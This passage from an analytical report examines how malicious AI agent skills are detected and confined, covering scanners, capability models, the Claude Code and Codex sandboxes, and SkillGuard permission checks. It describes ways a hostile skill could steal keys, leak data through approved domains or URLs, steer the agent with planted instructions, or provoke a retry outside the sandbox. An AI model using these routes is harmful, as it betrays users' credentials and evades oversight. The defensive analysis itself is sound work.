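Comparing a skill's code with its description depends on how much the description rules out. Suppose `pdf-text` said it "processes local files and connects to online services as needed". Reading the invoice and uploading it would both fit, and reading the user's login keys might too, since they are local files. He and colleagues try to prevent this by having the model look at the specific file or credential, but the model must still judge whether a loose phrase covers it. Twenty-three of SkillScope's 74 false alarms were disputes like this, where the text covered the general use of a service or secret but not the particular data flow or storage.

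Comparing a skill's description with its code gives authors an incentive to be vague. An author who writes a precise description but forgets to mention an access key gets flagged, while one who writes a vague description may pass. He and colleagues advise authors to state the resources a skill uses and the data it sends out, which is good advice for honest authors. A marketplace could also reject vague descriptions, but it would need a rule for what counts as vague, and the skill format doesn't supply one.

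A hostile author can also try to evade the checker. SkillScope's keyword rules already miss some ordinary calls, so a programmer who knows the rules could presumably avoid them on purpose. Work by He and colleagues assumes that skill authors are not trying to evade the tool, so its accuracy figures apply only to that case. Zhao and colleagues do assume a hostile author, but their scanner may still miss file names and addresses that the program builds only while running.

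Inspection before installation also misses code that arrives later through updates, external pages and dependencies. Pandey and colleagues found declared dependencies in 2,871 listings, and 2,830 of those listings had at least one dependency without a fixed version. Scanning each new version of a skill helps with updates. He and colleagues' tool would be practical for this because it needs only one language model call per skill once it has built the graph. But a new release of a library would not trigger another scan.

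A correct warning informs the user but does not limit what the skill's code can access. A marketplace can refuse to list a flagged skill, and a runtime could refuse to load it, but if the user installs it anyway, `extract.py` starts with the same access it would have had without the warning. The roughly three mismatched skills in every thousand that SkillScope would miss, by its own count, would also run with that access, and their users would get no warning.

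## What confining a skill to declared capabilities requires

To limit what `extract.py` can reach, a runtime first needs a statement of what the skill is supposed to reach. The skill format has no machine-readable field for this, although `allowed-tools` looks like one.

### The allowed-tools field

In the current specification, Agent Skills warns that support for this experimental field may vary between runtimes. The author lists tool names separated by spaces:

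```
allowed-tools: Bash(git:*) Bash(jq:*) Read
```

`Bash` runs shell commands, and the brackets narrow it to commands that start with `git` or `jq`, two common command-line programs. `Read` opens files.

The field's wording is ambiguous. The specification's summary table describes "pre-approved tools the skill may use", which could mean that the skill may use no others. The longer entry refers only to tools "that are pre-approved to run". Unofficial tutorials differ on the meaning. Claude with Skills' *Lesson 03* says the field spares the user permission prompts, while Claude Ninja's *Allowed Tools* calls it "a safety boundary" that stops a skill from doing anything the author hasn't listed. Willison (2025) called the specification under-specified and gave this field as one example.

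In Claude Code, `allowed-tools` pre-approves the listed tools without blocking others, so a user who believed Claude Ninja would wrongly think that `allowed-tools: Read` prevents a skill from running commands.

Other software may ignore the field, because the specification doesn't require a runtime to act on it. Li and colleagues report that Anthropic's Agent SDK, a toolkit for building agents, never reads the field, so a skill there gets whatever tools the developer's application grants. The toolkit has its own setting with a similar name, `allowed_tools`, which also only pre-approves the tools it lists. Anthropic warns that if a developer also turns on the mode that bypasses permission checks, the agent can use every unlisted tool. To restrict the agent's tools, a developer must name the ones to block or choose a mode that denies everything unlisted.

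Claude Code's users can also restrict tools by writing permission rules, giving a helper agent a shorter tool list, or installing hooks, which are programs that run before a tool call and can deny it. According to Anthropic, a hook's approval doesn't override a rule that denies the same call. So the runtime can enforce limits on tools, but the user or developer has to write them, usually without the skill's author having stated what the skill needs.

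### Why permission to use a shell says so little

Even if a runtime treated `allowed-tools` as a complete list and refused every other tool, the list would still describe a skill's access poorly, because it names the tools an agent can use but not the files or servers it can use them on.

`Bash(git:*)` includes permission to read many files and use the network, because `git push` sends the contents of a repository to whatever server the command names. For `pdf-text`, the author would need something like `Bash(python:*)`, since the agent starts the script with a Python command, and an unconfined Python program can access everything the account can. An entry that covers only `python scripts/extract.py` fixes which script runs but doesn't limit what the script can access.

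The optional `compatibility` field comes closer to naming resources. One of the specification's examples is "Requires git, docker, jq, and access to the internet". But this is a prose note for people, which a runtime can't enforce, and it doesn't name an address.

### Four requirements

Confinement requires a complete declaration that software can check. If the declaration for `pdf-text` omits the PDF library that the script loads, the runtime must either refuse the access and break the skill, or allow unlisted access and confine nothing. Complete declarations are realistic only when omissions have consequences. Authors have little reason to declare everything today, because a skill with an incomplete declaration works just as well.

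Confinement also requires that the script start without ambient authority, meaning the access it would otherwise inherit from the account it runs under. The runtime, or the system underneath it, has to remove that access and grant only what the skill declares.

A check must cover every action the skill takes, a principle that Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder named complete mediation in 1975. Hooks and permission rules in Claude Code apply only when the agent calls a tool, so they don't cover what a script, or any program it starts, does once running. The check therefore has to happen where programs get access to files and network connections, which on most computers is the operating system.

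Finally, the runtime has to attribute each action to a skill. A session might load both `pdf-text` and a skill that posts reports to the company's chat system, where only the chat skill has declared network access. The agent then issues a command that uploads the invoice's text. Nothing in the command identifies the skill that led to it, and the model may have drawn on both. If the runtime permits whatever either skill declared, `pdf-text` gains network access by sharing a session with the chat skill. Permitting only what both declared would prevent the chat skill from posting its reports.

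Claude Code illustrates the difficulty of attributing a tool call to a skill. According to Anthropic, a skill there adds no tool of its own, and the model loads it through a general Skill tool. The steps that follow are presumably ordinary calls to `Bash` or `Read`. Running each skill in a separate context would help. Li and colleagues describe an optional header field for this, `context: fork`, but the current specification doesn't list it, so it is probably an extension that only some runtimes support. Attribution is easier for bundled scripts, because the runtime knows which folder it started the script from.

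### Capabilities as pairs

*Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (Bhardwaj, 2026) formally models some of these requirements. It also presents SkillFortify, the scanner that labeled the malicious pptx_skill harmless in Zhao and colleagues' comparison.

The model builds on an old idea. In 1966, Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn proposed that a program should hold capabilities, which are references that it cannot forge and that combine a resource with a right to use it. Later work extended this into the object-capability model, in which such references are the only source of authority. Bhardwaj lists four ways for a program to get one:

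- It holds the reference from the start, as when a runtime launches `extract.py` with the invoice already open.
- It creates the resource itself, such as a temporary file.
- Its creator passes on some of its own references, as when `extract.py` starts a helper program and hands it the open invoice.
- Another program that holds the reference shares it.

In a capability-based programming language, a script can't gain access to the user's login keys by writing out their path, because a path is only text. In 2010, Sergio Maffeis, John Mitchell and Ankur Taly proved that untrusted code in such a language can't gain more authority than others give it. In ordinary Python, any script can try to open any file by path, so a skill's scripts need limits from outside the language.

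Bhardwaj writes a capability as a pair (*r*, *ℓ*). The first part, *r*, is one of eight types of resource: the file system, the network, environment variables (settings that often hold passwords), the shell, other skills, the clipboard, the browser and databases. The second part, *ℓ*, is a level of access:

NONE < READ < WRITE < ADMIN

Each level includes the ones below it, and ADMIN adds the right to give or withdraw other programs' access. Each skill *s* has a set of capabilities that its author declares, *Cap*<sub>D</sub>(*s*). Each action *a* has a required capability, *req*(*a*), which is the least access that would permit it. For example, reading a file requires (file system, READ), and running a shell command requires (shell, WRITE).

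The runtime refuses an action *a* unless skill *s* has declared a capability that covers the one *a* requires. If *req*(*a*) = (*r*, *ℓ*), then *Cap*<sub>D</sub>(*s*) must contain a pair (*r*, *ℓ*′) with *ℓ* ≤ *ℓ*′, which means the same resource type at the required level or higher.

When one skill calls another, the second may use only capabilities that the first also has, so a long chain of skills can't accumulate access. This is safe but sometimes inconvenient. If `pdf-text` called the chat skill to post its summary, the chat skill would lose its network access for that call because `pdf-text` has none.

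### The theorem, the scanner and the runtime

The confinement theorem has a static version, about a skill's files, and a runtime version, about what the skill does when it runs. Bhardwaj proves the static version. SkillFortify reads the files, infers what each operation it finds would require, and records the highest level required for each type of resource. According to the theorem, if the declared set covers this inferred set, no operation in the skill's code needs more than the author declared.

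The proof is short. Each operation's level is at most the highest one found, and the declared level is at least that high, so no operation exceeds the declared level. Bhardwaj then checks that sequences, branches, loops and function calls don't add operations that weren't already in the text.

All of this depends on the tool finding every operation and classifying it correctly. Bhardwaj acknowledges that the guarantee covers only the operations SkillFortify extracts: commands, references to environment variables, web addresses and embedded blocks of code. It wouldn't apply if `extract.py` assembled a command from fragments of text while running, or read a server's address from another file. The parser Bhardwaj describes works on the header, the instructions and the code embedded in them, so it may not read a separate script file at all.

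SkillFortify can also miss what a shell command does. It infers (shell, WRITE) from any command it recognises, and adds other pairs only if it also detects a web address, a file operation or something similar. A command like `./backup` could read a whole home directory and send it over the network, but SkillFortify would infer only shell access, so a skill that declared only shell access would pass.

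SkillFortify also compares the two sets only if a skill declares its capabilities. Bhardwaj's sample skills do this in header fields called `capabilities` and `permissions`, which the Agent Skills specification doesn't define. Skill authors could put the same information in the free-form `metadata` field, but no runtime has to read it there. For an ordinary skill without a declaration, the scanner only searches for suspicious patterns.

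The runtime version of the theorem is that no action a skill takes while it runs exceeds the declared set, provided that the skill has no ambient authority and cannot forge capabilities, and that the runtime applies the covering rule to every action. This follows almost immediately from the assumptions, and the difficulty is building a runtime in which they hold. Bhardwaj hasn't built one, and calls the result a design for future work. The model also has no way to attribute an action to a particular skill when several share a context, and Bhardwaj leaves the combined effects of skills for later.

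### What the benchmark measured

Bhardwaj tested the scanner on 540 program-generated examples, divided equally among Claude Code skills, OpenClaw skills and MCP server configurations. Half were malicious, and each of these contained one of 13 kinds of attack, such as stealing credentials or opening a remote connection for an attacker.

SkillFortify caught 250 of the 270 malicious examples and flagged none of the 270 harmless ones. Its precision was 100%, its recall was 92.6%, and its F1 score, which combines the two, was 96.15%. Twelve of the 20 misses involved deceptive names. Eight packages shared a name with a company's private package, and four had names that closely resembled a popular skill's. No scanner could recognise these from their contents alone, because it would need a list of the genuine names. Fourteen of the 20 misses were MCP configurations, which give a scanner much less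 text to examine.

The absence of false alarms is weak evidence of how the analysis would perform on real skills, because the harmless examples came from a generator designed to leave out anything suspicious. Real skills often run interpreters and contact servers for good reasons. Bhardwaj names this as the main doubt about the result and notes that the theorem doesn't explain the lack of false alarms. An analysis guaranteed to miss nothing should, if anything, raise more of them.

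Bhardwaj expected that tracking the flow of information would reveal attacks too spread out for any single pattern to match, but the rule written to do this added no detections. It looked for skills that both encode data and contact an outside address, and all 44 times it fired, pattern matching had already caught the skill. Bhardwaj can't tell whether the technique or the test set is to blame, because the set contained no example designed to distinguish the two explanations.

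All 250 detections therefore came from pattern matching. The benchmark measures how well SkillFortify recognises known kinds of attack. It provides almost no evidence about confinement, whether by comparing declared and inferred capabilities or by stopping a running program.

### A capability set for the PDF skill

Take the request to summarise `invoice.pdf`. In Bhardwaj's notation, the smallest declaration that lets `pdf-text` do this is

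*Cap*<sub>D</sub> = {(file system, WRITE), (shell, WRITE)}

The script reads the PDF and saves a text file, and WRITE covers both. The shell is included because the agent has to run a script to follow the instructions in `SKILL.md`.

A narrower set, made up of rights to specific resources, would look like this:

```
read:    the PDF that the user names
create:  one text file in the same folder
read:    Python and the PDF library
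```

It grants no network access, environment variables or other programs. The runtime starts the script itself, so the skill doesn't need the shell. Four actions show the difference:

| Action by `extract.py` | Required pair | Under Bhardwaj's pairs | Under the narrower set |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reads `invoice.pdf` | (file system, READ) | Allowed | Allowed |
| Reads the user's login keys | (file system, READ) | Allowed | Refused |
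| Sends the invoice to a server | (network, WRITE) | Refused | Refused |
| Starts `curl`, a program for transferring files | (shell, WRITE) | Allowed | Refused |

Reading the invoice requires the same pair as reading the login keys, because the pair contains no path. A runtime that followed Bhardwaj's rule exactly would therefore let the script read the keys, but it would stop the script from sending them anywhere, since `pdf-text` declares no network access.

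A skill with a good reason to use the network wouldn't face that obstacle. rankaj, the weather skill on ClawHub that sent the runtime's access keys to an outside address, needed to contact a weather service. A capability for the whole network would also have allowed the theft, but one limited to the weather service's address would have blocked it.

Bhardwaj's pairs allow starting `curl`, but sending the invoice with it also requires (network, WRITE). If the runtime's check extends to child processes, the runtime blocks the upload. If it covers only the agent's own commands, `curl` uploads the invoice.

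The narrower set is harder to write. When the author publishes `pdf-text`, the file `invoice.pdf` may not exist yet, so the declaration needs a placeholder like "the PDF that the user names", which the runtime must fill in for each request. Passing the script the open file is safer than passing a permitted path, because somebody could replace the file at that path with a link to the login keys. A fixed declaration must also cover folders of invoices and PDFs on the web, so it still grants too much for one local invoice.

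### Misuse of a granted capability

This kind of confinement would stop many of the known attacks. Cato's altered GIF skill had to download and run a program, and a skill that makes GIFs doesn't need to do either. The runtime would have blocked the download, and the user's files would have been safe even if the user had approved the skill without reading it.

But the runtime can only hold a skill to its declared set, and the skill's author writes that set. An author could declare ADMIN for all eight types of resource. The theorem would still hold, since no action could exceed that declaration, but the skill would have as much freedom as it has today. SkillFortify checks that a skill declares at least what it uses, but not that it declares only what it needs, as least privilege requires. Its installer can leave out skills that need more than a company permits, but the company first has to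 decide what to permit.

A reasonable declaration can also permit a harmful act. The chat skill needs to read reports and post messages to the company's chat service. With only those rights, it could post a confidential salary list to a channel that everyone reads. Both capabilities are legitimate, and the harm comes from sending that document to that channel. Preventing it requires a rule about which data may go where, as well as rules about which resources the skill may use.

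Bhardwaj claims that a skill that passes the static check "cannot exfiltrate data", within the model's assumptions. This seems too strong even under those assumptions. A skill that declares file reading and network writing can pass the check and still send the user's files to an outside server. Read-only network access can also leak data. In Bhardwaj's model, fetching a web page requires only (network, READ), but a script can put the text of an invoice into the address it requests, and the server's owner will receive it.

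Confining `extract.py` also doesn't stop the agent from following instructions in the text the script returns. The static guarantee doesn't cover this case, because Bhardwaj excludes attacks that depend on how a model interprets language.

### Narrow functions in place of a shell

Another approach is to give the agent no shell. In *Don't Prompt Your Agents. Equip Them*, Peilivanidis (2026) proposes Skillware, a format in which a skill is a fixed Python function with typed inputs. A Skillware bundle still includes instructions for the model, along with the code, a manifest that defines the inputs, and tests that run without a model. The model decides when to call the function and fills in the inputs, but it never writes code or commands.

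A Skillware version of `pdf-text` might offer one function, `extract_text(file)`. The agent would pass it the name `invoice.pdf`, Skillware would check that the input has the right type, and the function would return the text. If the invoice contained hidden instructions to upload the user's configuration files, the agent would have no function for uploading them unless another skill or the runtime provided one, whereas an agent with a shell could write the command itself.

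For actions that are hard to undo, such as a bank transfer, a function can offer a trial run and carry out the action only if the call includes `confirmed: true`. Peilivanidis presents this as a barrier that no prompt can bypass, but if the model fills in the value along with the other inputs, an attacker who can get it to make the transfer can presumably get it to confirm as well. To prevent this, the host program would have to set the value itself after asking the user.

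ChatGPT plugins had a similar interface, and Li and colleagues describe them as the only widely used extension format whose manifest limited the extension to a declared, reviewable set of actions. Skillware applies such a manifest to code on the user's own computer. As with plugins, someone has to write and maintain a function for every action. If the invoice is a scanned image and `extract_text` can't read it, the agent can't install a text-recognition program and continue. The user may want that restriction for an invoice, but people also use coding agents because they can improvise.

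Peilivanidis argues that the exchange improves reliability. In tests of 23 models under 368 conditions, small models with Skillware did better on complex tasks than much larger models without it, and made no errors filling in inputs. These results come from the project's own developer and cover accuracy and cost, not resistance to attack.

A typed interface limits what the model can ask for, but not what the function does once it starts. Peilivanidis relies on people reviewing the code in advance, and the tests check that a function keeps to its manifest. A function that extracted the text correctly but also sent a copy of the invoice to a stranger could pass tests that check only its inputs and outputs. Skillware functions appear to run inside the host program's process, since Skillware hands slow ones to worker threads there. The function would therefore succeed in sending the copy unless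 something outside that process blocked the connection.

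## Operating-system sandboxes around agents

The operating system can block a connection like that because programs must go through it to open files or reach the network. Before starting `extract.py`, a runtime can specify which files and network addresses the script may use, and the operating system blocks access to all others for as long as the script runs. These limits don't depend on the skill's description, so a false description doesn't give the script any extra access.

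The sandbox's limits also cover every program that the script starts, which permission prompts don't. If `extract.py` launches `curl` to upload the invoice, `curl` runs inside the same sandbox.

### One file read and one outbound connection

Suppose that a user on a Linux laptop has turned on Claude Code's sandbox, opened a session in the folder that holds `invoice.pdf`, and asked for a summary. Claude Code starts the script through bubblewrap, a Linux program that gives a command a restricted view of the computer. Under the default rules that Anthropic documents for version 2.1.285, a malicious `extract.py` would get this far:

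1. It opens the invoice. The file is in the working directory, where commands may read and write, so the operating system allows it.
2. It opens the user's login keys. They are outside the working directory, but the default rules restrict reading much less than writing. A command can read nearly the whole computer, so the script gets the keys.
3. It tries to send both to its author's server. The script runs in a private network with no link to the outside, and its only way out is a proxy, a relay program that Claude Code runs outside the sandbox. The proxy looks for the server's name in a list of allowed domains, which starts empty. In Manual mode, the script then waits while Claude Code asks the user about the server.

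If the user refuses, the invoice and the keys stay on the laptop. The script can't bypass the proxy, because a direct connection fails with an error such as "Network is unreachable".

The user also has more information than an ordinary permission prompt would give, since that would only name the script. Someone who wanted a local PDF summarised has good reason to wonder why the script needs a server.

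In the Cato demonstration, the altered GIF skill would have triggered a similar prompt when it tried to download MedusaLocker. If the ransomware had been in the skill's folder, it would not have needed the network and could have encrypted everything in the working directory. It could not have encrypted the user's files elsewhere, because the sandbox blocks writing there.

### What Claude Code and Codex allow by default

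Claude Code's sandbox is off until the user turns it on. Codex runs in a sandbox by default, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*.

| | Claude Code (version 2.1.285) | Codex (version 0.115 or later) |
|---|---|---|
| On by default | No | Yes |
| On a Mac | Seatbelt, the system's own sandbox | Seatbelt |
| On Linux | bubblewrap | bubblewrap and seccomp, which filters requests to the system's core |
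| On Windows | None, except inside the Linux environment WSL2 | OpenAI's own sandbox |
| A command can read | Nearly all files | Most files |
| A command can write to | The working directory, a temporary folder and folders the user adds | The workspace and temporary folders |
| Network | Closed until someone approves a domain | Closed |
| If a command needs more | Claude may retry it outside the sandbox | Codex asks for approval |

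Codex recommends a stricter, read-only mode for folders without version control, which is probably how most people store their invoices. In this mode, Codex asks before it edits a file or runs a command.

OpenAI built its own Windows sandbox after rejecting every existing option. It designed the first version to limit which folders a command could write to and to work without administrator rights. InfoQ (2026) describes a later version that runs commands under dedicated Windows accounts and controls their network access with firewall rules. The first version remains as a fallback with weaker network isolation.

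Claude Code and Codex also differ in what they do when sandboxing fails. If bubblewrap is missing, Claude Code runs commands without a sandbox unless the user has set it to stop. On a Mac, Codex refuses to run a command if it can't enforce the limits on it, according to OpenAI's *Permissions*. Codex's choice is safer, since a user who turned on a sandbox presumably wants to know when it isn't there.

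When a command fails inside Claude Code's sandbox, Claude can ask to run it again outside the sandbox. In Manual mode the user sees a prompt marked "unsandboxed", and in auto mode the classifier decides. But if the user has a rule that allows the command, the retry needs no approval. Many users have such rules for Python, so in Manual mode `extract.py` could run outside their sandbox without a prompt. A hostile script might encourage a retry by printing an error that attributes its failure to the sandbox, though Claude would still have to choose to retry. Users can disable these retries with one setting.

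By default, Codex asks the user to approve requests to leave the sandbox, but users can have a reviewer model answer them instead. An approved command runs outside the sandbox's limits.

Users can weaken either sandbox much further:

- Claude Code's users can list commands that always run outside the sandbox, or turn off the file rules and keep only the network rules. If they bypass permission checks, the sandbox also lets commands reach any server that the user hasn't explicitly blocked, unless a stricter network setting is on.
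- Codex's users can turn off the sandbox and all approvals with one option, which has the short name `--yolo`. They can also open the network alone. Unless they turn on Codex's filtering proxy as well, every command can then contact any server.

Neither sandbox covers everything an agent does. Claude Code's sandbox covers shell commands, while the built-in tools for reading files and fetching web pages follow separate permission rules. If the user forbids sandboxed commands to read the login keys, Claude's own file-reading tool can still open them. This matters when a skill's instructions tell the agent to misuse its access, because the agent may not need to run a script to do so. Codex likewise has separate controls for MCP servers, connected apps and the browser.

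Anthropic lets users confine all of Claude Code by running it in a container, a virtual machine or a separate tool called the sandbox runtime, which is still a research preview. Anthropic says that the sandbox for shell commands isn't enough by itself when nobody is supervising the agent.

### Effects on prompts and on work

According to Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, sandboxed commands need fewer permission prompts. This is because Claude Code automatically approves most sandboxed commands by default, even in Manual mode, where edits made with Claude's file-editing tool would still need approval.

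Fewer prompts may help people pay attention to the ones that remain. But a drop in prompts doesn't measure how many attacks a sandbox stops or how many tasks it breaks, and few measurements of either seem to have been published.

Replacing approval prompts with a sandbox seems to help with actions outside the sandbox's boundary, because the operating system blocks what a tired user might have approved. Inside the boundary, the user loses the safeguard of the prompt. In Manual mode without a sandbox, a user might notice a command that deletes a folder of invoices. With the sandbox on, the same command can usually run without a prompt if the folder is in the working directory. A few deletions that could do exceptional damage still require approval.

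According to Anthropic's documentation, the container program Docker doesn't work in the sandbox, and neither do most database clients, because they ignore the proxy. On a Mac, Git can't download or upload code over SSH, a common type of connection, even if the user has allowed the server. Anthropic's usual remedy is to run the affected program outside the sandbox, where it has the user's full access, so people whose work depends on such programs get the least protection.

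### A boundary around the session

Neither product normally gives each skill its own boundary. Suppose again that a session includes both `pdf-text` and the skill that posts reports to the company's chat service. When the chat skill first runs, Claude Code prompts the user to allow the service's domain, and the user agrees. If the user chooses "Yes", the domain stays open for the rest of the session. If they choose not to be asked again, it stays open in later sessions too. `extract.py` can now also reach the chat service, although it has no reason to do so to extract text.

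An invoice sent to a service that the company already uses can still end up outside the company, because the proxy approves the domain without checking which account receives the data. If the chat service also serves other customers, the author of `extract.py` can open an account there, put that account's access key in the script, and have it post the invoice to a channel outside the company.

Codex's older network setting has an even broader effect. If a user turns on network access for the chat skill without the filtering proxy, `extract.py` can also reach every server on the internet. Newer permission profiles, still in beta, can limit commands to particular domains, but OpenAI describes a profile as the default for the whole session. Codex also has a separate setting for approving skill scripts, but it treats the scripts of all skills as one category.

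In Claude Code, subagents (helper agents with their own context) use the same sandbox settings as the session that started them. Running a skill in a subagent therefore doesn't further restrict which files and servers its commands can reach.

Claude Code's auto mode has come closer to a narrower boundary since version 2.1.271, which lets Claude attach a list of servers to a single sandboxed command. The classifier reviews the list along with the command, and if it approves, those servers are open only while the command runs. The chat skill can post its report, and the chat service is closed again when Claude later starts `extract.py`. Because access is granted to a command rather than a skill, a skill could still gain access if its instructions led Claude to request a server and the classifier approved. The restriction also applies only if the user has turned on the sandbox, which auto mode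 doesn't require.

OpenAI tried per-skill permissions in Codex's code in early 2026. In February it let skill authors use an `openai.yaml` file to list the folders and network access a skill needs. By 26 February, Codex could run a skill's script under exactly those permissions, which OpenAI noted might be stricter than the session's. On 5 March OpenAI (2026) changed the rule so that a skill's permissions add to the session's.

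Under the February rule, `pdf-text` could have declared one folder and no network, and its script would have had no network access even in a session where the chat skill did. Under the March rule, the script gets everything the session allows plus anything extra the skill declares, so an author's list can only widen access. The change may have made skills more reliable, because a script no longer breaks when its author forgets to declare something the session already permits.

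Both rules applied to one particular way Codex ran shell commands. It is unclear whether the feature still exists, since OpenAI now describes `openai.yaml` as a file for a skill's "appearance and dependencies".

### A hosted container

A hosted container is separate from the user's laptop, so `extract.py` can't read login keys that nobody has copied into the container, whatever the file rules allow.

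Codex's cloud service runs each job in two phases, in a container managed by OpenAI. During setup, the container can use the network to install software, such as the PDF library that `extract.py` needs. The agent then starts without network access, unless the user has enabled it for that environment. Before the agent starts, the service removes any passwords or keys that the user supplied for setup.

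This order suits `pdf-text` because the script needs the internet only to download its library. It doesn't protect against a malicious library, whose code may run during setup, when both the network and the supplied keys are available.

Anthropic runs Claude Code's cloud sessions in a virtual machine with its own operating-system kernel. The machine connects to the network through a proxy with a default list of allowed domains. Anthropic keeps the user's GitHub token, which gives access to their code, outside the machine and supplies a more limited credential inside it.

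Hosting shifts the risk to whatever data the user sends to the container. For example, the user has to send the invoice there before the script can read it. Skills used in the same job also share a container, so the boundary is still around the whole session, though the session contains much less.

### What a script can still reach

A sandbox has to leave the script enough access to do its job, and a hostile script can misuse that access.

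Project files are the most exposed, because `extract.py` can change or delete any ordinary file in the working directory, including programs. OpenAI warns that a user or tool may later run such a file outside the sandbox, where the altered code has the user's full access. Both products protect some obvious targets. Codex makes its own settings folder and Git's data read-only. Claude Code stops commands from changing its settings, shell startup files and the folders that hold skills, so a sandboxed script can't rewrite `SKILL.md` there. But its published list of protected paths doesn't include a project's `CLAUDE.md`, so a script may still be able to leave instructions there for later sessions.

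Claude Code has no built-in list of credential files to protect, so a script can read any keys the user hasn't blocked. Blocking the script's network access doesn't fully protect the keys, because the script can print one in its output. The key then enters the model's context, and `SKILL.md` could contain a malicious instruction to include it in a web address that Claude fetches. Claude's web tool runs outside the sandbox, so the user's permission rules would have to stop the request. Even without an attack, anything Claude reads goes to Anthropic or whichever company runs the model.

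A program can also leak data through approved destinations. Anthropic gives github.com as an example of a domain broad enough to create a risk, since anyone can have an account there. The proxy also relies on the server name the program supplies and doesn't normally inspect encrypted traffic, so a program may be able to name an approved server while sending its data to another on the same infrastructure.

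Sandboxes also have bugs, and attackers look for them. Anthropic says its sandbox reduces risk but "is not a complete isolation boundary". A virtual machine provides stronger separation than a sandbox on the user's own system, because an attacker who takes over its kernel still has to escape the virtual machine to reach the user's system.

### When a useful skill needs broad access

The strongest practical complaint about sandboxing is that it blocks access many skills need to be useful. A skill that posts reports needs access to a server and a credential, and one that manages Docker containers needs a program that can't run inside Claude Code's sandbox. Users who keep running into such failures may turn the sandbox off.

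The complaint doesn't apply to every skill. Only about a third of the listings that Pandey and colleagues scanned showed signs of sending data over the network. Some of the others will need to download something, but many, such as `pdf-text`, would probably have little trouble with a closed network.

A skill that needs a credential may not need to hold it. Claude Code can give sandboxed commands a placeholder instead of a real access key. When a command sends a request to an approved server, the proxy replaces the placeholder with the key. The chat skill can then post its report without having the key. Anthropic, as quoted by Willison, says that credentials that never enter the sandbox "can't be exfiltrated". The user has to set this up, and it depends on an experimental feature that decrypts traffic. The skill can still do whatever the key permits on the approved server, so a key with few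 rights is safer.

Users can narrow file access too. A Codex profile for working on invoices might look like this, supposing that the skill is in a folder called `skills`:

```
default_permissions = "invoices"

[permissions.invoices]
extends = ":workspace"

[permissions.invoices.filesystem]
":root" = "deny"
":minimal" = "read"
"~/skills/pdf-text" = "read"
```

The profile starts from the usual rules, which let commands write in the current folder and block network access. It then denies access to the rest of the disk, except for the skill's own folder and the files that common tools need. `extract.py` can read the invoice but not the login keys. It can also read every other file in the invoice's folder, so invoices are best kept in a separate folder. If the PDF library is in an unusual place, the script will fail until the user adds another line to the profile.

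This profile grants close to the narrow set of rights that `pdf-text` needs, and Codex can enforce it today. But the user had to work out what the skill needs because its author never declared it, and the profile also applies to every other skill in the session.

For skills that need broad access, a disposable environment may be the best option. The user can start a container or virtual machine, put in only the files for one job, and delete the environment afterwards. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* recommends separate environments for workloads that must not share data. If each skill ran in its own environment, the session's boundary would also isolate that skill, without any change to the skill format.

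This works well for a batch of invoices but badly for a task that combines skills. Someone who wants `pdf-text` to read an invoice and the chat skill to post the summary would have to copy the text from one environment to the other. It is also no use for a skill that has to change the user's own computer, such as one that cleans up old files across the home folder. That skill must be able to delete from the folders the user most wants to protect, so a malicious version could do almost as much damage there inside a sandbox as it could without one.

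## Permission checks while a skill runs

A sandbox applies the same limits to a command regardless of which skill led to it or what the user asked for. Researchers have tried to account for the skill and the request with two kinds of check. One limits each skill to a fixed list of permitted actions, so that `pdf-text` can never upload a file. The other limits a skill to what the current request needs, so that a skill with permission to post reports posts one only when the user wants it posted.

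### A permission list for each skill

Pan, Sun and colleagues (2026), in *SkillGuard*, describe a system of fixed lists modelled on Android's app permissions. Each skill comes with a manifest, a machine-readable list of the permissions it asks for. One for `pdf-text` might look roughly like this:

```
{
  "skill_metadata": { "name": "pdf-text" },
  "permissions": [
    { "capability": "file.read", "effect": "allow",
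      "constraints": { "workspace_only": true } },
    { "capability": "file.write", "effect": "allow",
      "constraints": { "workspace_only": true } },
    { "capability": "shell.execute", "effect": "confirm" }
  ]
}
```

Each entry names a type of action and an effect, which is `allow`, `confirm` (ask the user) or `deny`. Constraints can narrow an entry, in this case to files in the workspace. They can also limit it to certain paths or rule out certain commands. Conflicts between entries are settled by priority.

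The permissions come from a fixed vocabulary that covers 21 kinds of resource in eight groups: storage, code repositories, the network, running programs, hardware, system settings, secrets, and the agent's own tools and rules. To test it, Pan and colleagues took 1,260 skills from the SkillsMP marketplace, 20 from each of its 63 categories. Two of the researchers marked every instruction that told the agent to act on a particular resource. They found such instructions in 784 of the skills, and the vocabulary had a term for 1,407 of the 1,408 resources they recorded.

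Authors would therefore nearly always have a word for what their skill does. But the test doesn't show that the words are narrow enough. A permission to send data to the web, for example, covers every site.

### From a tool call to a decision

SkillGuard works through hooks, so Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI can use it without changes to their code. Suppose a user asks for a summary of `invoice.pdf`, and `extract.py` secretly uploads a copy.

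1. When the session starts, SkillGuard creates a record of the session's permissions and fills it with the default rules for the workspace.
2. When the agent loads `pdf-text`, SkillGuard adds the entries from the skill's manifest.
3. The agent issues the command `python scripts/extract.py invoice.pdf`. Before the runtime carries it out, SkillGuard translates the call into its own vocabulary, here `shell.execute`, and looks for an entry that covers it.
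4. The entry's effect is `confirm`, so the user can allow the command once, allow it for the session, or refuse. Approval for the session keeps the entry's constraints, so it can't open more folders than the manifest did.
5. If the user agrees, a second model reads the command and the script, and lists the more specific permissions that they will need. It notices the upload, which needs `web.post`.
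6. SkillGuard checks this list against the record as well. The manifest doesn't mention `web.post`, so SkillGuard blocks the command. It would also block the command if the second model's analysis failed.

Pan and colleagues are inconsistent about undeclared permissions. In one passage, the user decides whether to allow the action, but in another, and in their worked example, SkillGuard blocks it. Blocking is safer because a tired user may approve the request.

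Bhardwaj's confinement theorem relies on the same rule, that a declared permission must cover every action. SkillGuard applies the rule to tool calls, but for a script it relies on the second model's prediction. If the upload is in a library that the script loads, the model may miss it, and SkillGuard cannot stop it once the script starts. Pan and colleagues also mention only scripts in the workspace, so it is unclear whether the model would read a skill installed in the user's home folder. A sandbox with a closed network would block the upload in all these cases.

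### Control of what enters the context

Text alone can steer an agent, so SkillGuard has a separate permission for loading outside content into the context, which Pan and colleagues classify as dangerous. Related permissions cover handing work to another agent, changing the runtime's rules and installing hooks.

AIR's landing-page skill sent the agent to an online manual that AIR later replaced with malicious instructions. With this permission, SkillGuard could at least ask the user before the manual reached the model. But the permission only controls whether text enters the context, not what the model does after reading it. A legitimate skill that uses a manual also needs the same permission.

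Pan and colleagues didn't test this part separately. Only two of the 1,408 resources they recorded in marketplace skills were of this kind, so there is little evidence of how the control would work in practice.

### Attacks that still succeed

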